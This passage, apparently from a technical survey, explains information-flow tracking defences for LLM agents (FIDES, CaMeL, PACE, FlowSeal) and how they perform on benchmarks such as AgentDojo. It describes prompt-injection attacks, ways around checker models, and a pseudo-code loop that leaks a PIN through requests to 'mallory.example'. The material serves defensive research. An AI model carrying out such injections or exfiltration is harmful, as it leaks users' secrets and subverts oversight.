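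Nonmalleable information flow combines the two limits. Attackers may not influence a declassification, and a system may not endorse data that its supplier could not have read. The name comes from cryptography, where an encryption scheme is malleable if someone can turn one encrypted value into a related one.

These limits also make exceptions easier to review. Kanniwadi and Myers gave a machine-checked proof that if a program passes their type checker, an attacker with broad access to its untrusted data can achieve no more than one who can interact with it only where it lowers a label. Reviewers can therefore concentrate on those places. The proof covers programs in a small language built for the purpose, so an agent would get the same benefit only if its tracker covered the rest of the agent's behavior as completely as the type checker covers the rest of a program.

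In Garby and colleagues' language for agents, endorsement is an explicit operation that a reviewer can search for. A value endorsed in an untrusted context stays untrusted. They found one way around that limit. If a program endorses the text of an email and then has a model write code based on it, the new code runs in a trusted context, so endorsements in that code take effect. To block such chains, they suggest marking every endorsed value and refusing to endorse anything that already has the mark.

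### Yes-or-no answers from untrusted text

Costa and colleagues propose a different kind of exception for FIDES, based on how much information an answer can hold. They arrange output types in a lattice:

yes or no ⊑ a choice from a fixed list ⊑ free text

When the planner queries the quarantined model, it specifies the answer's type. Constrained decoding enforces the type by letting the model produce only text that fits a given format. The type becomes part of the answer's label, and a join takes the higher type along with the higher security label. A policy can then allow an untrusted yes-or-no answer where it would block untrusted text, because a yes-or-no answer cannot contain a planted instruction.

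In the paper's example, a user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and to create a calendar event if it finds one. The emails stay in a variable. The quarantined model answers yes or no, and the planner inspects only that answer. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the details into a second variable, which the planner passes to the calendar tool without reading it.

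An answer with n possible values carries at most log₂ n bits:

| Type of answer | Possible values | Maximum in bits |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Yes or no | 2 | 1 |
| One of three actions | 3 | 1.6 |
| Four-digit number | 10,000 | 13.3 |
| Free text | No fixed number | No fixed limit |

Garby and colleagues stress that the list of options has to be fixed in advance, because an attacker who could add options could also raise the limit. They also object that nobody can tell from a given run whether a small value that passed was a harmless exception or a leak. Most AgentDojo tasks did not need constrained decoding, so Costa and colleagues did not use it in their tests, and their results provide little evidence of how well this exception works.

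Even if each answer reveals little, a series of answers can reveal a whole secret. Suppose the company lets employees ask Ana's assistant yes-or-no questions about her files, and one file contains a four-digit PIN. Dev, who may not read the file, asks whether the PIN is at least 5000, then halves the remaining range with each further question. There are 10,000 possible PINs, and fourteen answers can distinguish 2¹⁴ = 16,384 numbers, so fourteen questions always identify the PIN. If the policy also allows questions with ten possible answers, Dev needs only four, one for each digit.

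The type sets the maximum information an answer can reveal, and many answers reveal far less. If Dev asks whether the PIN is 1234 and the answer is no, he has ruled out one number in 10,000 and learned about 0.00014 bits. He might need 9,999 questions to find the PIN. Sabelfeld and Sands observe that an equality test can still reveal an entire secret, though more slowly, when the attacker chooses the guesses.

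To stop Dev, the application would have to keep a running total of its answers about each secret. Even a limit of ten answers would let him narrow the PIN to about ten possibilities. The total must also carry over between sessions. If the application counts separately for each employee, Dev and a friend can pool their answers. If it keeps one count for everybody, Dev can use up the answers his colleagues need for honest questions. Garby and colleagues point to a similar build-up in CaMeL, where each attempt at a task can reveal whether the policy blocked it, and a retry loop outside the tracker allows enough attempts to extract a whole secret.

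Even a single answer can do harm if the planner has attached a harmful action to it. Costa and colleagues suggest that the quarantined model could choose from a list such as scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply or forwarding an email. With three options, Mallory has at most 1.6 bits of influence over the choice, which is enough to select "forward". If the planner pays an invoice whenever the answer is "yes", Mallory needs only one bit to trigger the payment. The `x` in Myers and colleagues' program is also a single bit, and its value determines whether the program releases the secret.

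Counting bits therefore limits how many outcomes an attacker can choose between, but not how bad the worst one is. A company could reasonably accept an untrusted "yes" for adding a calendar entry that Ana can delete, but refuse it for payments and declassification.

### Who may authorise an exception

Some useful values are too varied for any short list. Garby and colleagues' banking agent pays bills using account numbers and amounts from untrusted files. Its planner writes the necessary endorsements into a program before it sees any file. Garby and colleagues justify this by arguing that a user who asks the agent to pay the bill in a file has chosen to trust that file. With endorsement, the agent completed 36 of 48 test runs using the model Qwen3.7-plus and 31 using MiMo-v2.5, compared with 30 and 26 without it, a difference well within the margin of error. No attack succeeded on either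 model, with or without endorsement. But the user's request only permits the agent to use the file's account number and doesn't verify it, so the agent will pay Mallory if she has forged the bill.

**A fixed policy** is the easiest authority to defend. The company writes it before any attack, ordinary code applies it, and nothing in Mallory's email can change it. A rule that employees may share unmarked incoming mail with colleagues would let Ana's summary reach Ben without a confirmation prompt. But the company must foresee each exception, and a broad rule will sometimes release something Ana would have kept back. The policy's conditions also need trusted inputs. If a rule applies only "after the board has approved the budget", the application must check the board's own records rather than search Ana's inbox for the word "approved".

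**The user** can judge cases that no policy foresaw. When the application asks Ana whether to send the summary to Ben, her "yes" is a declassification, even if the prompt doesn't call it that. Costa and colleagues warn that frequent prompts cause confirmation fatigue and give attackers a chance to manipulate the user. Claude Code users approve 93% of requests, but most requests are presumably legitimate, so this rate alone doesn't show that users are careless. The relevant figure is the share of malicious requests that they refuse.

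The evidence is clearer that some people switch the prompts off. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on the code editor Cursor, in which a planted ticket in the issue tracker Jira led the agent to leak secrets from a developer's computer. The attack worked only if the developer had disabled confirmation for the Jira tool or turned on Cursor's Auto Run mode, which minimizes prompts.

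Fewer and better prompts would help. Kolluri and colleagues reduce the number of prompts by having the agent plan around the labels, though some tasks will still need the user's approval, as many did in the RTBAS tests. The application should also write the prompt itself, from the labels and the actual call, because an explanation from the assistant might repeat Mallory's claim to be the auditor. With a prompt such as "Send Budget to Mallory, who is not a permitted reader", Ana can judge the actual request.

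**A checker model** could review the summary for anything confidential from Mallory's email, and the application could declassify the summary if the model found nothing. But the checker has to read the summary, including any instructions Mallory has planted in it. Under FIDES's rules, the checker's yes-or-no answer is untrusted because it is derived from untrusted text, so letting it decide whether to release a secret violates robust declassification. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* adds that there is no exact specification to check such a model against, and that attackers have bypassed pairs of models and guards by attacking each part separately. A checker is more useful if it can block a release the policy would allow but cannot approve one the policy forbids.

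**The tool or the agent** might simply state that its output is clean. Suppose Ana's assistant passes the budget sheet through an outside supplier's redaction tool, which returns a page of text labelled "public":

| Step | Permitted readers | Basis for the label |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The sheet enters the agent | Ana, Ben, Chloe | The sheet's access list |
| The application sends it to the redaction tool | Ana, Ben, Chloe | The tracker's own record |
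| The tool returns the redacted text | Everyone | The supplier's statement |
| The assistant emails the text to Mallory | Everyone | The supplier's statement |

The tracker works correctly in the first two steps, but the last step relies on a declared label, just as it would without tracking. If the tool missed a salary, or its publisher lied, the policy engine still approves the message. The system also relies on a declared label if the assistant can mark its own text as safe by calling a function. Restricting that function to trusted contexts would keep Mallory from influencing the decision, but the label would still depend on the model's assessment of its own text.

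An application can check that an answer is "yes" or "no", or that a result is a single number, without trusting whatever produced it. It has no comparable test for whether a page of text contains anything confidential. A company that needs redaction can instead write a function that returns only the budget's total, have its own developers review the code, and name that function in the policy as the only place where budget data may become public.

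## What tracking guarantees and which flows it misses

Even if the company lets budget data become public only through one reviewed function, it still needs to know whether the tracker blocks every other route. That depends on what counts as a leak, which researchers define by comparing runs of the same program on different secret inputs.

### Noninterference and explicit secrecy

In 1982 Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer introduced a strict security condition called noninterference. An agent satisfies it if any two runs that differ only in their secret data look the same to an outsider. Any visible difference violates the condition, even if the outsider never receives a copy of a secret.

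In the notation of Costa and colleagues, slightly simplified, d₁ and d₂ are two versions of all the data that the agent's tools can reach, and d₁ ≈ d₂ means that they contain the same public data. The function g₁ is the combined effect of the steps the agent takes when it starts from d₁, and g₂ is the effect of the steps it takes from d₂. Noninterference requires

d₁ ≈ d₂ ⟹ g₁(d₁) ≈ g₂(d₂)

Costa and colleagues' system, FIDES, aims for a weaker property called explicit secrecy, which Daniel Schoepe and colleagues proposed in 2016 for taint tracking:

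d₁ ≈ d₂ ⟹ g₁(d₁) ≈ g₁(d₂)

The formulas for noninterference and explicit secrecy differ in one subscript. Noninterference compares what the agent would do with each of two versions of the data. Explicit secrecy takes the steps from one run, applies them to both versions and compares the public results. If a step publishes the budget sheet on a web page, the two versions produce different pages, so the agent violates explicit secrecy. But explicit secrecy doesn't cover what an outsider could learn from the agent's choice of steps.

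Costa and colleagues state that their tracking loop can enforce explicit secrecy. They define the property precisely and prove a supporting lemma, but they don't include a proof for the loop itself.

For integrity, the comparison changes the untrusted data instead. Noninterference then requires that the trusted results stay the same whatever Mallory writes.

### A leak without a copy

Suppose a confidential file records whether the board has approved a takeover in the United States. Ana tells her assistant to look up the dollar exchange rate if the board has approved the takeover, and otherwise to check the weather for her holiday. Both lookup tools fetch a public web page and take no arguments.

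| Board's decision | Tool the assistant calls | What an outsider sees |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Approved | Exchange rate | A visit to the currency site |
| Not approved | Weather | A visit to the weather site |

The assistant sends no secret to either site, but anyone who can see which site it visits learns the board's decision. This is an implicit flow, in which the choice of action reveals the data.

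The assistant still satisfies explicit secrecy. When the board has approved the takeover, the only step an outsider can see is the assistant's visit to the currency site, and that step would produce the same visit if it were applied to the other version of the file. The assistant violates noninterference, however, because it would have visited the weather site if it had read the other version.

The permitted-flow rule doesn't catch this either, because it checks only the labels of a call's arguments, and these calls have no arguments. It doesn't use the label on the call itself, which the trusted-action rule uses to check integrity.

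Each choice between two tools reveals one bit, and a series of choices can spell out a longer secret, as Dev's yes-or-no questions did.

### Is the leak small enough to accept?

Costa and colleagues accept implicit flows because they consider full noninterference too restrictive. In their view, once an agent has called a tool that may read secrets, noninterference would essentially forbid it from calling any tool that may write public data. Ana's assistant, for example, would be unable to look up a postcode on the web after opening the budget sheet. Costa and colleagues expect an outsider who sees the sequence of calls to learn only limited information, and they note that TaintDroid and web browsers make the same compromise.

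The ban can be narrower if the planner never reads the secret. If FIDES keeps the board's decision in a variable, the planner chooses its later calls without knowing the decision, so its choice cannot reveal it. A company could then forbid publicly visible calls only when the planner's context is secret. The assistant could still search the web, but it could not carry out Ana's request, which requires choosing a tool based on the decision. The FIDES experiments hid only untrusted data and did not test such a rule.

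Garby and colleagues doubt that the leak stays small. Agents mix data and control: a model's reply may be a piece of text or a program to run, and what the agent reads can determine what it does next. They argue that leaks through control flow can then be very efficient. Suppose a planted instruction leads an agent to write this program:

```
for guess in 0 to 9999:
    if guess == pin:
        open_page("mallory.example/" + guess)
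```

The program builds the web address from `guess`, a counter that isn't copied or calculated from the PIN. A tracker that follows only copying and calculation therefore labels the address public. But the PIN determines which value of `guess` the program sends, so a single request gives Mallory the whole PIN.

FIDES is less exposed to this trick because its planner writes one call at a time, and anything it writes after reading the PIN inherits the PIN's label. Mallory would have to encode the PIN in the choice of tools or of public values the application had stored earlier. The objection applies more strongly to agents that write whole programs.

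FIDES's formal definition of explicit secrecy also has a gap that its tracker doesn't have. The definition treats the tools' stored data as data, but the conversation as part of the control. Suppose the assistant reads the PIN 1234, then posts "1234" on a public page. The formula represents this step as "post 1234", with the argument already fixed. That step would still post 1234 if the stored PIN were 5678, so the public results match and the definition is satisfied even though the PIN leaked.

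The policy engine would block this post because the argument carries the PIN's label. But a proof of explicit secrecy in this form would not rule out the simplest leak an agent can cause.

### Labelling control flow

Garby and colleagues track control flow in the LLMbda calculus, their small language for writing agents. Alongside the labels on values, the interpreter keeps a program-counter label, written pc, for the decisions that led to the code it is now running:

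1. The program starts with pc at the bottom of the lattice.
2. When a value with label m determines which code runs next, the interpreter runs that code with the label pc ⊔ m.
3. Everything that the code produces gets at least that label.
4. When the code finishes, the interpreter restores the earlier pc.

In the PIN program, the comparison `guess == pin` is secret, so the address built inside the `if` is secret too. A web tool that accepts only public data would refuse that address. Ana's two lookups would also run with a secret pc, and the tool could refuse both. Replacing pc ⊔ m with pc in the rule for calling functions is enough to make the interpreter ignore control flow, as ordinary taint tracking does.

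Conversations with a model need an extra rule. Suppose a program tells the model that the answer is "no", then tells it that the answer is "yes" only if the board has approved the takeover. The program then asks the model for the answer.

The interpreter stops any program that tries to add to a public conversation because of a secret decision, a rule called "no high upgrade". Raising the conversation's label when the program sends the extra message would not be enough. If the board has approved the takeover, the conversation would become secret and the answer "yes" would get a secret label. But if the board hasn't, the program sends no extra message, so the conversation stays public and the answer "no" gets a public label. Anyone who may read public data would then learn that the board hasn't approved the takeover.

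### What the calculus guarantees

The original February 2026 version of the paper proves noninterference for programs that finish. If two such programs differ only in parts that an observer at a given level isn't allowed to see, the observer can't distinguish their results or conversations.

In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, a user asked an agent to find the sender's address in the latest email and send that person a meeting reminder. The email contained a false notice that the meeting was cancelled. An ordinary tool-calling agent sent a cancellation. An agent that wrote its program before reading the email sent the reminder. The reminder's subject and body were labelled trusted, and its address was labelled untrusted.

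That test involved one malicious email, but the theorem extends the result to all others. If the same program finishes, changing the email can't alter the message's subject or body, because both have trusted labels. The theorem doesn't cover the address, so a different email could still cause the reminder to go to the wrong person.

A July 2026 revision contains a proof checked by computer in Lean. The proof applies to the actual code of the interpreter that runs the paper's examples, not just to a description of it. This rules out mistakes that a reviewer could easily miss, such as treating untrusted values as trusted once a program inserts them into a longer text.

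A weaker theorem covers programs that use endorsement. It guarantees that the exception affects only the part of the label that the program endorsed. For example, endorsing an account number does not make a secret public.

Even checking a label can leak information. Suppose a confidential envelope contains either an ordinary note or a top-secret one. Publicly disclosing whether the note is top secret reveals something about the envelope's contents. But a policy engine has to check labels and act on the results. With more than two levels, the February theorem therefore restricts how programs test labels. For example, they may use an assertion, which stops the program if the label is too high.

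### The cost of stopping programs

The "no high upgrade" rule sometimes stops a program that would not have leaked anything. Stopping can also reveal a secret. In the takeover example, the program stops if the board has approved the deal and finishes if it hasn't, so anyone who can see whether it finished learns the decision. The theorem allows this because it compares only runs that finish, a limitation called termination insensitivity.

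If an outsider sees only whether one run finishes, the leak is one bit, but it can be larger if the outsider sees the agent's actions as they happen. *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*, a 2008 paper by Sands and three other researchers, describes this larger leak. An agent's program could request public pages numbered 0, 1, 2 and so on, then deliberately break a rule when the number matches the PIN, which stops the run. The last page requested would reveal the PIN. This method is much slower than the single request in the earlier program, because a four-digit PIN takes up to 10,000 requests and each extra digit multiplies that maximum by ten.

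Developers also have to keep untrusted text out of the agent's main conversation, as CaMeL does. Garby and colleagues add that models have not been trained on their language, whereas CaMeL's planner writes familiar Python, and that a program cannot catch an information-flow error and try something else.

The LIO library, which Zhou and colleagues use for their agents, handles control flow more coarsely. Once a computation reads a secret, its current label stays raised until the computation ends. If every web request counts as sending data out, LIO would block both of Ana's lookups. Reading the file in a subagent would not help, because the assistant would have to open the subagent's sealed answer to choose a lookup.

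### The model as a mathematical function

Costa and colleagues treat the model as a deterministic function, which always gives the same reply to the same conversation and list of tools. Real models' replies are usually partly random, so two runs may differ even when the secrets are identical. Garby and colleagues made the same assumption in February, defending it as the right way to ask what would have happened if only the secret had been different.

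Their July revision drops the assumption and compares probabilities instead. If a program always finishes, changing the secrets doesn't change the probability of any public result. If it sometimes fails to finish, the probabilities before and after the change can differ by at most the average of the two chances of not finishing.

Both versions still assume that the model's reply depends only on the conversation. If a provider had trained the model on the company's payroll, the model could state a salary in a conversation labeled public. The tracker would not raise the label, because the salary never passed through the tracker.

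The proofs hold however the model turns conversations into replies. They cover a dishonest or incompetent model, including one that obeys every instruction Mallory plants.

### Flows that neither property covers

Neither property covers timing. Suppose Mallory asks Ana's assistant about a free afternoon, and it answers in two seconds when Ana's calendar is empty but takes twenty when it has to work through confidential meetings. Even if the reply is the same in both cases, Mallory learns something from the delay. Message length can also reveal information, since encryption hides the words but usually not roughly how many there are. Costa and colleagues explicitly leave out timing and the length of network packets.

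The proofs also take the starting labels as given. Costa and colleagues suggest that a system could relabel an untrusted document as trusted after a classifier finds no prompt injection in it, though they warn against relying too much on such detectors. If the classifier misses an attack, the tracker will carry the wrong label through every later step, and the theorem will no longer protect Ana even though it still holds.

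Data can also leave by a route that the tracker does not check. Zhou and colleagues require the whole application, including the code that retries failed attempts, to be in the language that enforces the rules. They cite a bug reported in Claude Code in March 2026, in which the program checked only the first part of a command joined by `&&` against its list of forbidden commands. An agent that can run Python could also use it to open a forbidden file without running any command on the list. Even Haskell, the language Zhou and colleagues chose, has functions that bypass its usual restrictions, so they limit agents to Safe Haskell, a subset without those functions.

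An attacker can also do harm by changing only the text that the user reads. One AgentDojo attack tells a travel assistant to recommend a certain place because it is gorgeous. Costa and colleagues do not try to stop this, because the assistant makes the same tool calls and reveals no secrets. The text keeps its untrusted label, so the application could mark it on the screen or withhold it. AgentDojo's test for whether this attack succeeded is crude. It looks for matching text, so an assistant can fail just by quoting a hotel review, as Garby and colleagues note.

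The harm can still be serious. Suppose Ana asks the assistant to compare three suppliers, and text hidden in Mallory's offer makes the summary favour Mallory. The application labels the summary correctly and the assistant makes no unusual calls, but Ana reads it and places the order herself.

False content can also reach a tool through an exception the system allows. In two of Garby and colleagues' test runs with GPT-5.2, the user asked the agent to make a payment described in a file, but an attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The agent endorsed the contents and paid the attacker. Without endorsement, the label check blocked the payment.

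### Why declared labels have no comparable theorem

A policy based on declared labels has the same problems with timing, message length, wrong source labels, unchecked routes and misleading text, but it compares better on implicit flows. A rule that forbids all outside communication after the agent has read private data would block both of Ana's lookups, provided that the file tool's label declares private data and the lookup tools' labels declare outside communication. This rule is crude and close to the ban that Costa and colleagues rejected as too restrictive, but it would stop a leak that their permitted-flow rule allows.

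The theorem is missing because of how a tracker's proof works. The proof shows that each step gives a new value a label at or above the labels of everything that influenced it. If this holds for every kind of step, it holds for the whole run.

When a publisher declares the label of a tool's output, the system does not compute that label from the tool's inputs. Any proof that the policy works would therefore have to assume that every tool declares everything it does, and Shi and colleagues found tools that do not.

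Enforced tracking also depends on conditions, such as correct source labels and accurate lists of what each tool reads and writes, but the company can write these conditions down and review them before the agent runs. Some of them may be declarations, and the proof still holds for the steps in between. For example, if servers declare the labels on their results and the application joins those labels itself, the proof shows that the application carries them correctly.

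The argument doesn't extend to labels that the agent reports. A theorem about those labels would have to assume that the model still reports its sources accurately after reading Mallory's email, whereas the proofs for enforced tracking hold even if the model gives false reports whenever Mallory tells it to.

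## Measured security and cost of enforced tracking

Ana's company needs measurements to know how many attacks a tracker stops in practice and how many ordinary tasks the agent still finishes, because a proof about labels does not establish either. Most researchers who measure this use AgentDojo, a benchmark that Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues released in 2024.

### The AgentDojo benchmark

AgentDojo simulates an office workspace, a travel service, a bank and the chat service Slack. Costa and colleagues count 97 user tasks and 36 injection tasks. A user task might be to book a hotel in Paris if its rating is above 4. An injection task is something an attacker might want, such as adding an outsider to the company's Slack.

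Each test pairs a user task with an injection task from the same setting and plants the attacker's instructions in data that the agent will read. Short programs then check whether the agent achieved the user's goal and whether it achieved the attacker's. The number of pairs depends on the benchmark version. Zhong and colleagues ran 629, and Girrens and Wang ran 949. All the extra pairs are in the workspace setting.

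The trackers' own evaluations mostly used an attack called "tool knowledge", in which the planted text names the tools the attacker wants the agent to call. AgentDojo has no labels of its own, so each development team decides which data is untrusted and which tools are consequential. Two trackers with the same score may therefore have enforced quite different rules.

### FIDES with and without its checks

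Costa and colleagues tested FIDES with GPT-4o. The table gives the number of attacks they judged to be real successes and the share of tasks completed, averaged over the four settings.

| Agent | Successful attacks | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed, under attack |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Unprotected | 152 | 84% | 72% |
| Plain tracking with checks | 0 | 42% | 39% |
| All untrusted data hidden, no checks | 0 | 47% | 44% |
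| FIDES without checks | 21 | 61% | 52% |
| FIDES with checks | 0 | 50% | 50% |

Without checks, FIDES's planner could inspect untrusted variables and then continue as usual, which let 21 attacks through. The best defence without guarantees that Costa and colleagues compared, in which a model removes unneeded tools before starting, performed about the same, letting 20 through.

An agent that could never inspect untrusted data stopped every attack without any checks. Its 47% completion rate somewhat overstates its ability, because the planner sometimes guessed. In the travel tasks, for example, it recommended the right hotel without seeing any ratings.

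Costa and colleagues report that FIDES completes 8% more tasks than a basic planner with plain tracking when both have their checks on. With checks on, FIDES has a task completion rate 34 percentage points lower than the unprotected agent's. The gap narrows to 22 points under attack because attacks also keep the unprotected agent from finishing its work.

The 34 points have two causes. Working with variables costs 24 points even with the checks off, because GPT-4o confuses variable names or forgets to use the quarantined model. The checks cost the other 11 or so. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, the costs change places:

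| Tasks completed, no attack | GPT-4o | o1 |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Unprotected | 84% | 84% |
| FIDES without checks | 61% | 78% |
| FIDES with checks | 50% | 61% |

A better model can complete most of the tasks lost to the use of variables, but not tasks that the policy forbids. Costa and colleagues expect FIDES, under the policies they used, to complete only tasks whose steps don't depend on the data. These make up about 56% of the banking tasks and 57% of the Slack tasks, and FIDES with o1 completed 56% and 54%. In those two settings, completing more tasks would mainly require different policies, or exceptions such as yes-or-no answers, which they left out of their tests.

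Hiding data sometimes reduces the number of tasks an agent completes. With GPT-4o, plain tracking completed 73% of travel tasks, while FIDES, which hides data in variables, completed 41%. Many travel tasks use tools that the policy allows even after the agent has read untrusted data, as long as nothing confidential leaks. An agent with plain tracking could use these tools freely, while one with FIDES still had to handle variables. The gap was smaller with o1, with plain tracking completing 75% and FIDES 68%.

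### Limits of the zero

Costa and colleagues labelled as untrusted exactly the fields that AgentDojo's attacks use, so the tracker had correct labels everywhere an attack would appear. The developers of Ana's assistant would not have a list of the fields attackers will use. If they wrongly marked a field as trusted, an attacker who found it could get past the trusted-action rule.

Zhong and colleagues labelled the data for RTBAS more realistically, marking all text from external sources as untrusted without looking at individual test cases. RTBAS still blocked every attack that broke its policy. In one workspace test, however, it did not track a possible injection because the injection was in text written by the user, which carried a trusted label. Blocking every policy-breaking attack therefore doesn't depend entirely on FIDES's convenient labels, but someone must still label each source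 correctly.

The zero also reflects a manual review. AgentDojo's own programs counted three successes against FIDES with checks and about twenty against plain tracking. Costa and colleagues examined these cases and rejected all of them, for three reasons:

- AgentDojo sometimes counts an attack as soon as the agent requests a tool, even if the policy engine then refuses the call.
- The policy allowed some of the attackers' actions, such as creating a calendar event with no other participants.
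- Some attacks changed only the text of the answer, which FIDES does not try to prevent.

Only the first of these is clearly a scoring error. In the calendar case, the attacker did get the event onto Ana's calendar, and she might not want strangers adding even harmless entries. The result is best read as "no attack broke the policy", a weaker claim than "no attacker achieved anything".

Girrens and Wang found the same scoring problem. In their extended version of AgentDojo, where one session covers several requests, SPA with label checks had an attack success rate of 0.2%, or about two runs in 949. They describe two runs that AgentDojo counted as successful attacks even though SPA had rejected the plan before any tool ran.

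### Other trackers and newer models

GPT-4o and o1 are old models, so their scores are weak evidence of how well a current agent would cope with variables and restrictions. CaMeL's published result comes from o3, which is also old. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports that CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks, compared with 84% without protection, and allowed no successful attacks of the kind it is designed to stop. CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens as the unprotected agent.

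Li and colleagues, who built PACE, produced more recent figures for CaMeL by running it for comparison on three models from 2026. Each arrow in the table goes from the result without the protection to the result with it. For PACE and the CaMeL reruns, attack success is the highest rate among three attack types.

| System | Model | Attack success | Tasks completed |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| CaMeL, published result | o3 | none within its threat model | 84% → 77% |
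| CaMeL, rerun by Li and colleagues | Qwen-3.8-27B | 48% → 0.3% | 63% → 35% |
| CaMeL, rerun by Li and colleagues | DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 99.8% → 28% | 76% → 60% |
| CaMeL, rerun by Li and colleagues | gpt-5.6-luna | 100% → 36% | 74% → 57% |
| RTBAS with a judge | GPT-4o | none that broke its policy | 10% lower without an attack, under 1% lower with one |
| SPA, label checks off → on | gpt-5.4-nano | 0.4% → 0% | 53% → 29% |
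| PACE | Qwen-3.8-27B | 48% → 0% | 63% → 60% |
| PACE | DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 99.8% → 5.1% | 76% → 75% |
| PACE | gpt-5.6-luna | 100% → 8.1% | 74% → 72% |

Some of Li and colleagues' other results suggest that not every defence was working as designed. Spotlighting, a method that marks untrusted text in the prompt, raised attack success on Qwen from 48% to 98%. On WASP, a benchmark of web tasks, FIDES with the same model completed none of the users' tasks, yet 40% of attacks succeeded in its worst category, compared with 19% for the unprotected agent. A working tracker should not do worse than no protection, so the adaptation of FIDES to WASP may have been faulty. A similar fault could explain CaMeL's 28% and 36%. Until CaMeL's developers or an independent group repeat the test, these figures are weak evidence that newer models make CaMeL less secure.

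Another rerun tested CaMeL on AgentDyn, a benchmark with harder and more dynamic tasks. CaMeL completed at most 4% of the tasks on any of the three models. This result is easier to believe, because a planner that has to write its whole program in advance could be expected to struggle with such tasks.

SPA's planner never reads what the tools return, even with label checks off, so the "off" figure doesn't describe an ordinary agent. That restriction alone left only four successful attacks in 949 runs, all against a single banking task. Turning on the label checks eliminated those four but lowered task completion by 24 percentage points. The checks stopped 53% of runs before any tool ran, and only 37% of runs got as far as executing their plan, compared with 81% without the checks.

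SPA and the FIDES variant that hid all untrusted data both suggest that very few of AgentDojo's attacks are left for labels to stop once the planner can't read the attacker's text. Labels are needed more for problems such as a forged account number on an invoice or a summary sent to the wrong colleague. AgentDojo's planted instructions test these problems much less, so its scores probably understate the benefits of label checks while fully reflecting their drawbacks.

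RTBAS reduced task completion only a little on average, but much more on Slack tasks, where completion fell to 22% with the judge and 33% with the attention screener. Many of those tasks involve reading an untrusted website and acting on it. Zhong and colleagues skipped every call that broke the policy instead of asking a simulated user. With a user who approved legitimate calls, RTBAS would have completed more tasks but shown more prompts.

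PACE has the best combination of scores in the table, but Li and colleagues' tests of its parts suggested that most of its security comes from checking calls against the user's request, not from tracking data. PACE reduced task completion by no more than three points on the full AgentDyn benchmark, but on a sample of 60 AgentDyn tasks, the share completed fell from 67% to 33%. Li and colleagues also wrote rules for each benchmark, using its public tool descriptions and task formats. A company would have to write similar rules for its own tools.

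Tracking can also run in a proxy between an agent and its MCP servers. *PrISM* (Anderson, 2026), a Princeton senior thesis, describes a proxy that tracks untrusted data and uses a separate detector to look for poisoned tool descriptions. On InjecAgent, another benchmark of planted instructions, the proxy reduced the worst-case attack success rate from 67.75% to 0.13%. Anderson notes that the agent could do less without a person's help with the proxy in place.

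### Attackers who know the defence

All the AgentDojo results above come from attacks written before the defence existed. Narisetty and colleagues warn that testing against fixed attacks has misled researchers before, since most of the twelve defences that failed in *The Attacker Moves Second* had looked strong in such tests. As of June 2026, no one had independently tested the systems that enforce rules outside the model in a way comparable to that paper.

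Attacks also succeed more often when the attacker can make repeated attempts. Narisetty and colleagues cite Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5, a 2025 model, in coding tasks. An adaptive attacker succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. A benchmark that runs each attack once would have reported only the 4.7% rate.

When ordinary code decides whether to allow an action, an attacker who persuades the model must still find a harmful action that the policy permits or a piece of data with the wrong label.

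Narisetty and colleagues tested this on Progent, which limits the tools and arguments an agent may use but does not track labels. With the small model Qwen2.5-7B, Progent reduced the average success rate of AgentDojo's fixed attacks from 25.8% to 4.2%. An attack they wrote with Progent's rules in mind succeeded 2.6% of the time, no better than the fixed attacks, so it may have been weak. They used one handwritten template and did not try automated methods that exploit access to the model's internals, so they describe the result as consistent with their hypothesis, not as proof of it.

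Li and colleagues automated the search for attacks on PACE. A second copy of Qwen-3.8-27B was given the agent's tool calls and PACE's reasons for refusing them, and it wrote four new attack texts per round, with up to 50 attempts per target. It succeeded on 21 of 30 targets against the unprotected agent and on none against PACE. The 95% confidence interval for PACE's failure rate runs from 0% to 11.4%. The attacks often hijacked the model even with PACE in place. The agent tried to make the attacker's call 157 times, and PACE blocked every one.

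However, the choice of targets favoured PACE. Li and colleagues first identified the 375 of 629 AgentDojo pairs that involved a call the user's request did not authorise, then drew all 30 targets from them. In the other 254 pairs (40%), the check on the user's authority would not by itself have stopped the attacker's call. An attacker who understood PACE would concentrate on those pairs, but the search included none of them.

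*Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) reports a larger test of a simpler defence. An automated attacker tried to extract secrets from models over hundreds of rounds, learning from each response. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually failed. A filter in the application's code, which checked each response before the user received it, leaked nothing in 15,000 attacks. This supports enforcing rules in code, but it doesn't measure how well a tracker would resist attacks, because the filter did not track labels or control tools.

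### Cooperation and enforcement in FlowSeal

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) comes closest to comparing protection that relies on the agent with protection that doesn't. It presents FlowSeal, a defense against people who trick an agent into revealing private data without planting any instructions. In one attack, an outsider shares a document and asks the agent to fill in its section. The agent treats this as ordinary teamwork and writes a confidential diagnosis in the document. In another, the outsider lists true and false records and asks the agent to delete the false ones, which leaves only the true ones.

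FlowSeal has two layers. The cooperative layer shows the agent which records are private and gives it tools for requesting the owner's consent, but the agent may fail to use them. The mandatory layer is code that intercepts every attempt to write or share data. If the recipient isn't already approved, the code sends the relevant private records and the proposed text to a separate model, which returns "safe" or "blocked".

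Shim and colleagues switched off parts of FlowSeal and repeated the shared-document attack in 105 scenarios, three times each, with the model DeepSeek-V3.2. They measured the share of private items that leaked and, separately, the share of harmless requests the agent fulfilled.

| Configuration | Private items leaked | Harmless requests fulfilled |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Neither layer, only a privacy prompt | 52.2% | 44.7% |
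| Cooperative layer only | 28.4% | 81.2% |
| Mandatory layer only | 8.8% | 74.4% |
| Both layers | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Both layers, but the checker allows everything | 24.9% | 79.4% |
| Both layers, but the checker blocks everything | 1.3% | 0% |

The mandatory layer alone leaked less than a third as much as the cooperative layer alone. Adding the cooperative layer to the mandatory layer reduced leakage further, from 8.8% to 0.5%. One likely reason is that an agent that knows which records are private includes them less often, so the checker has fewer chances to make a mistake.

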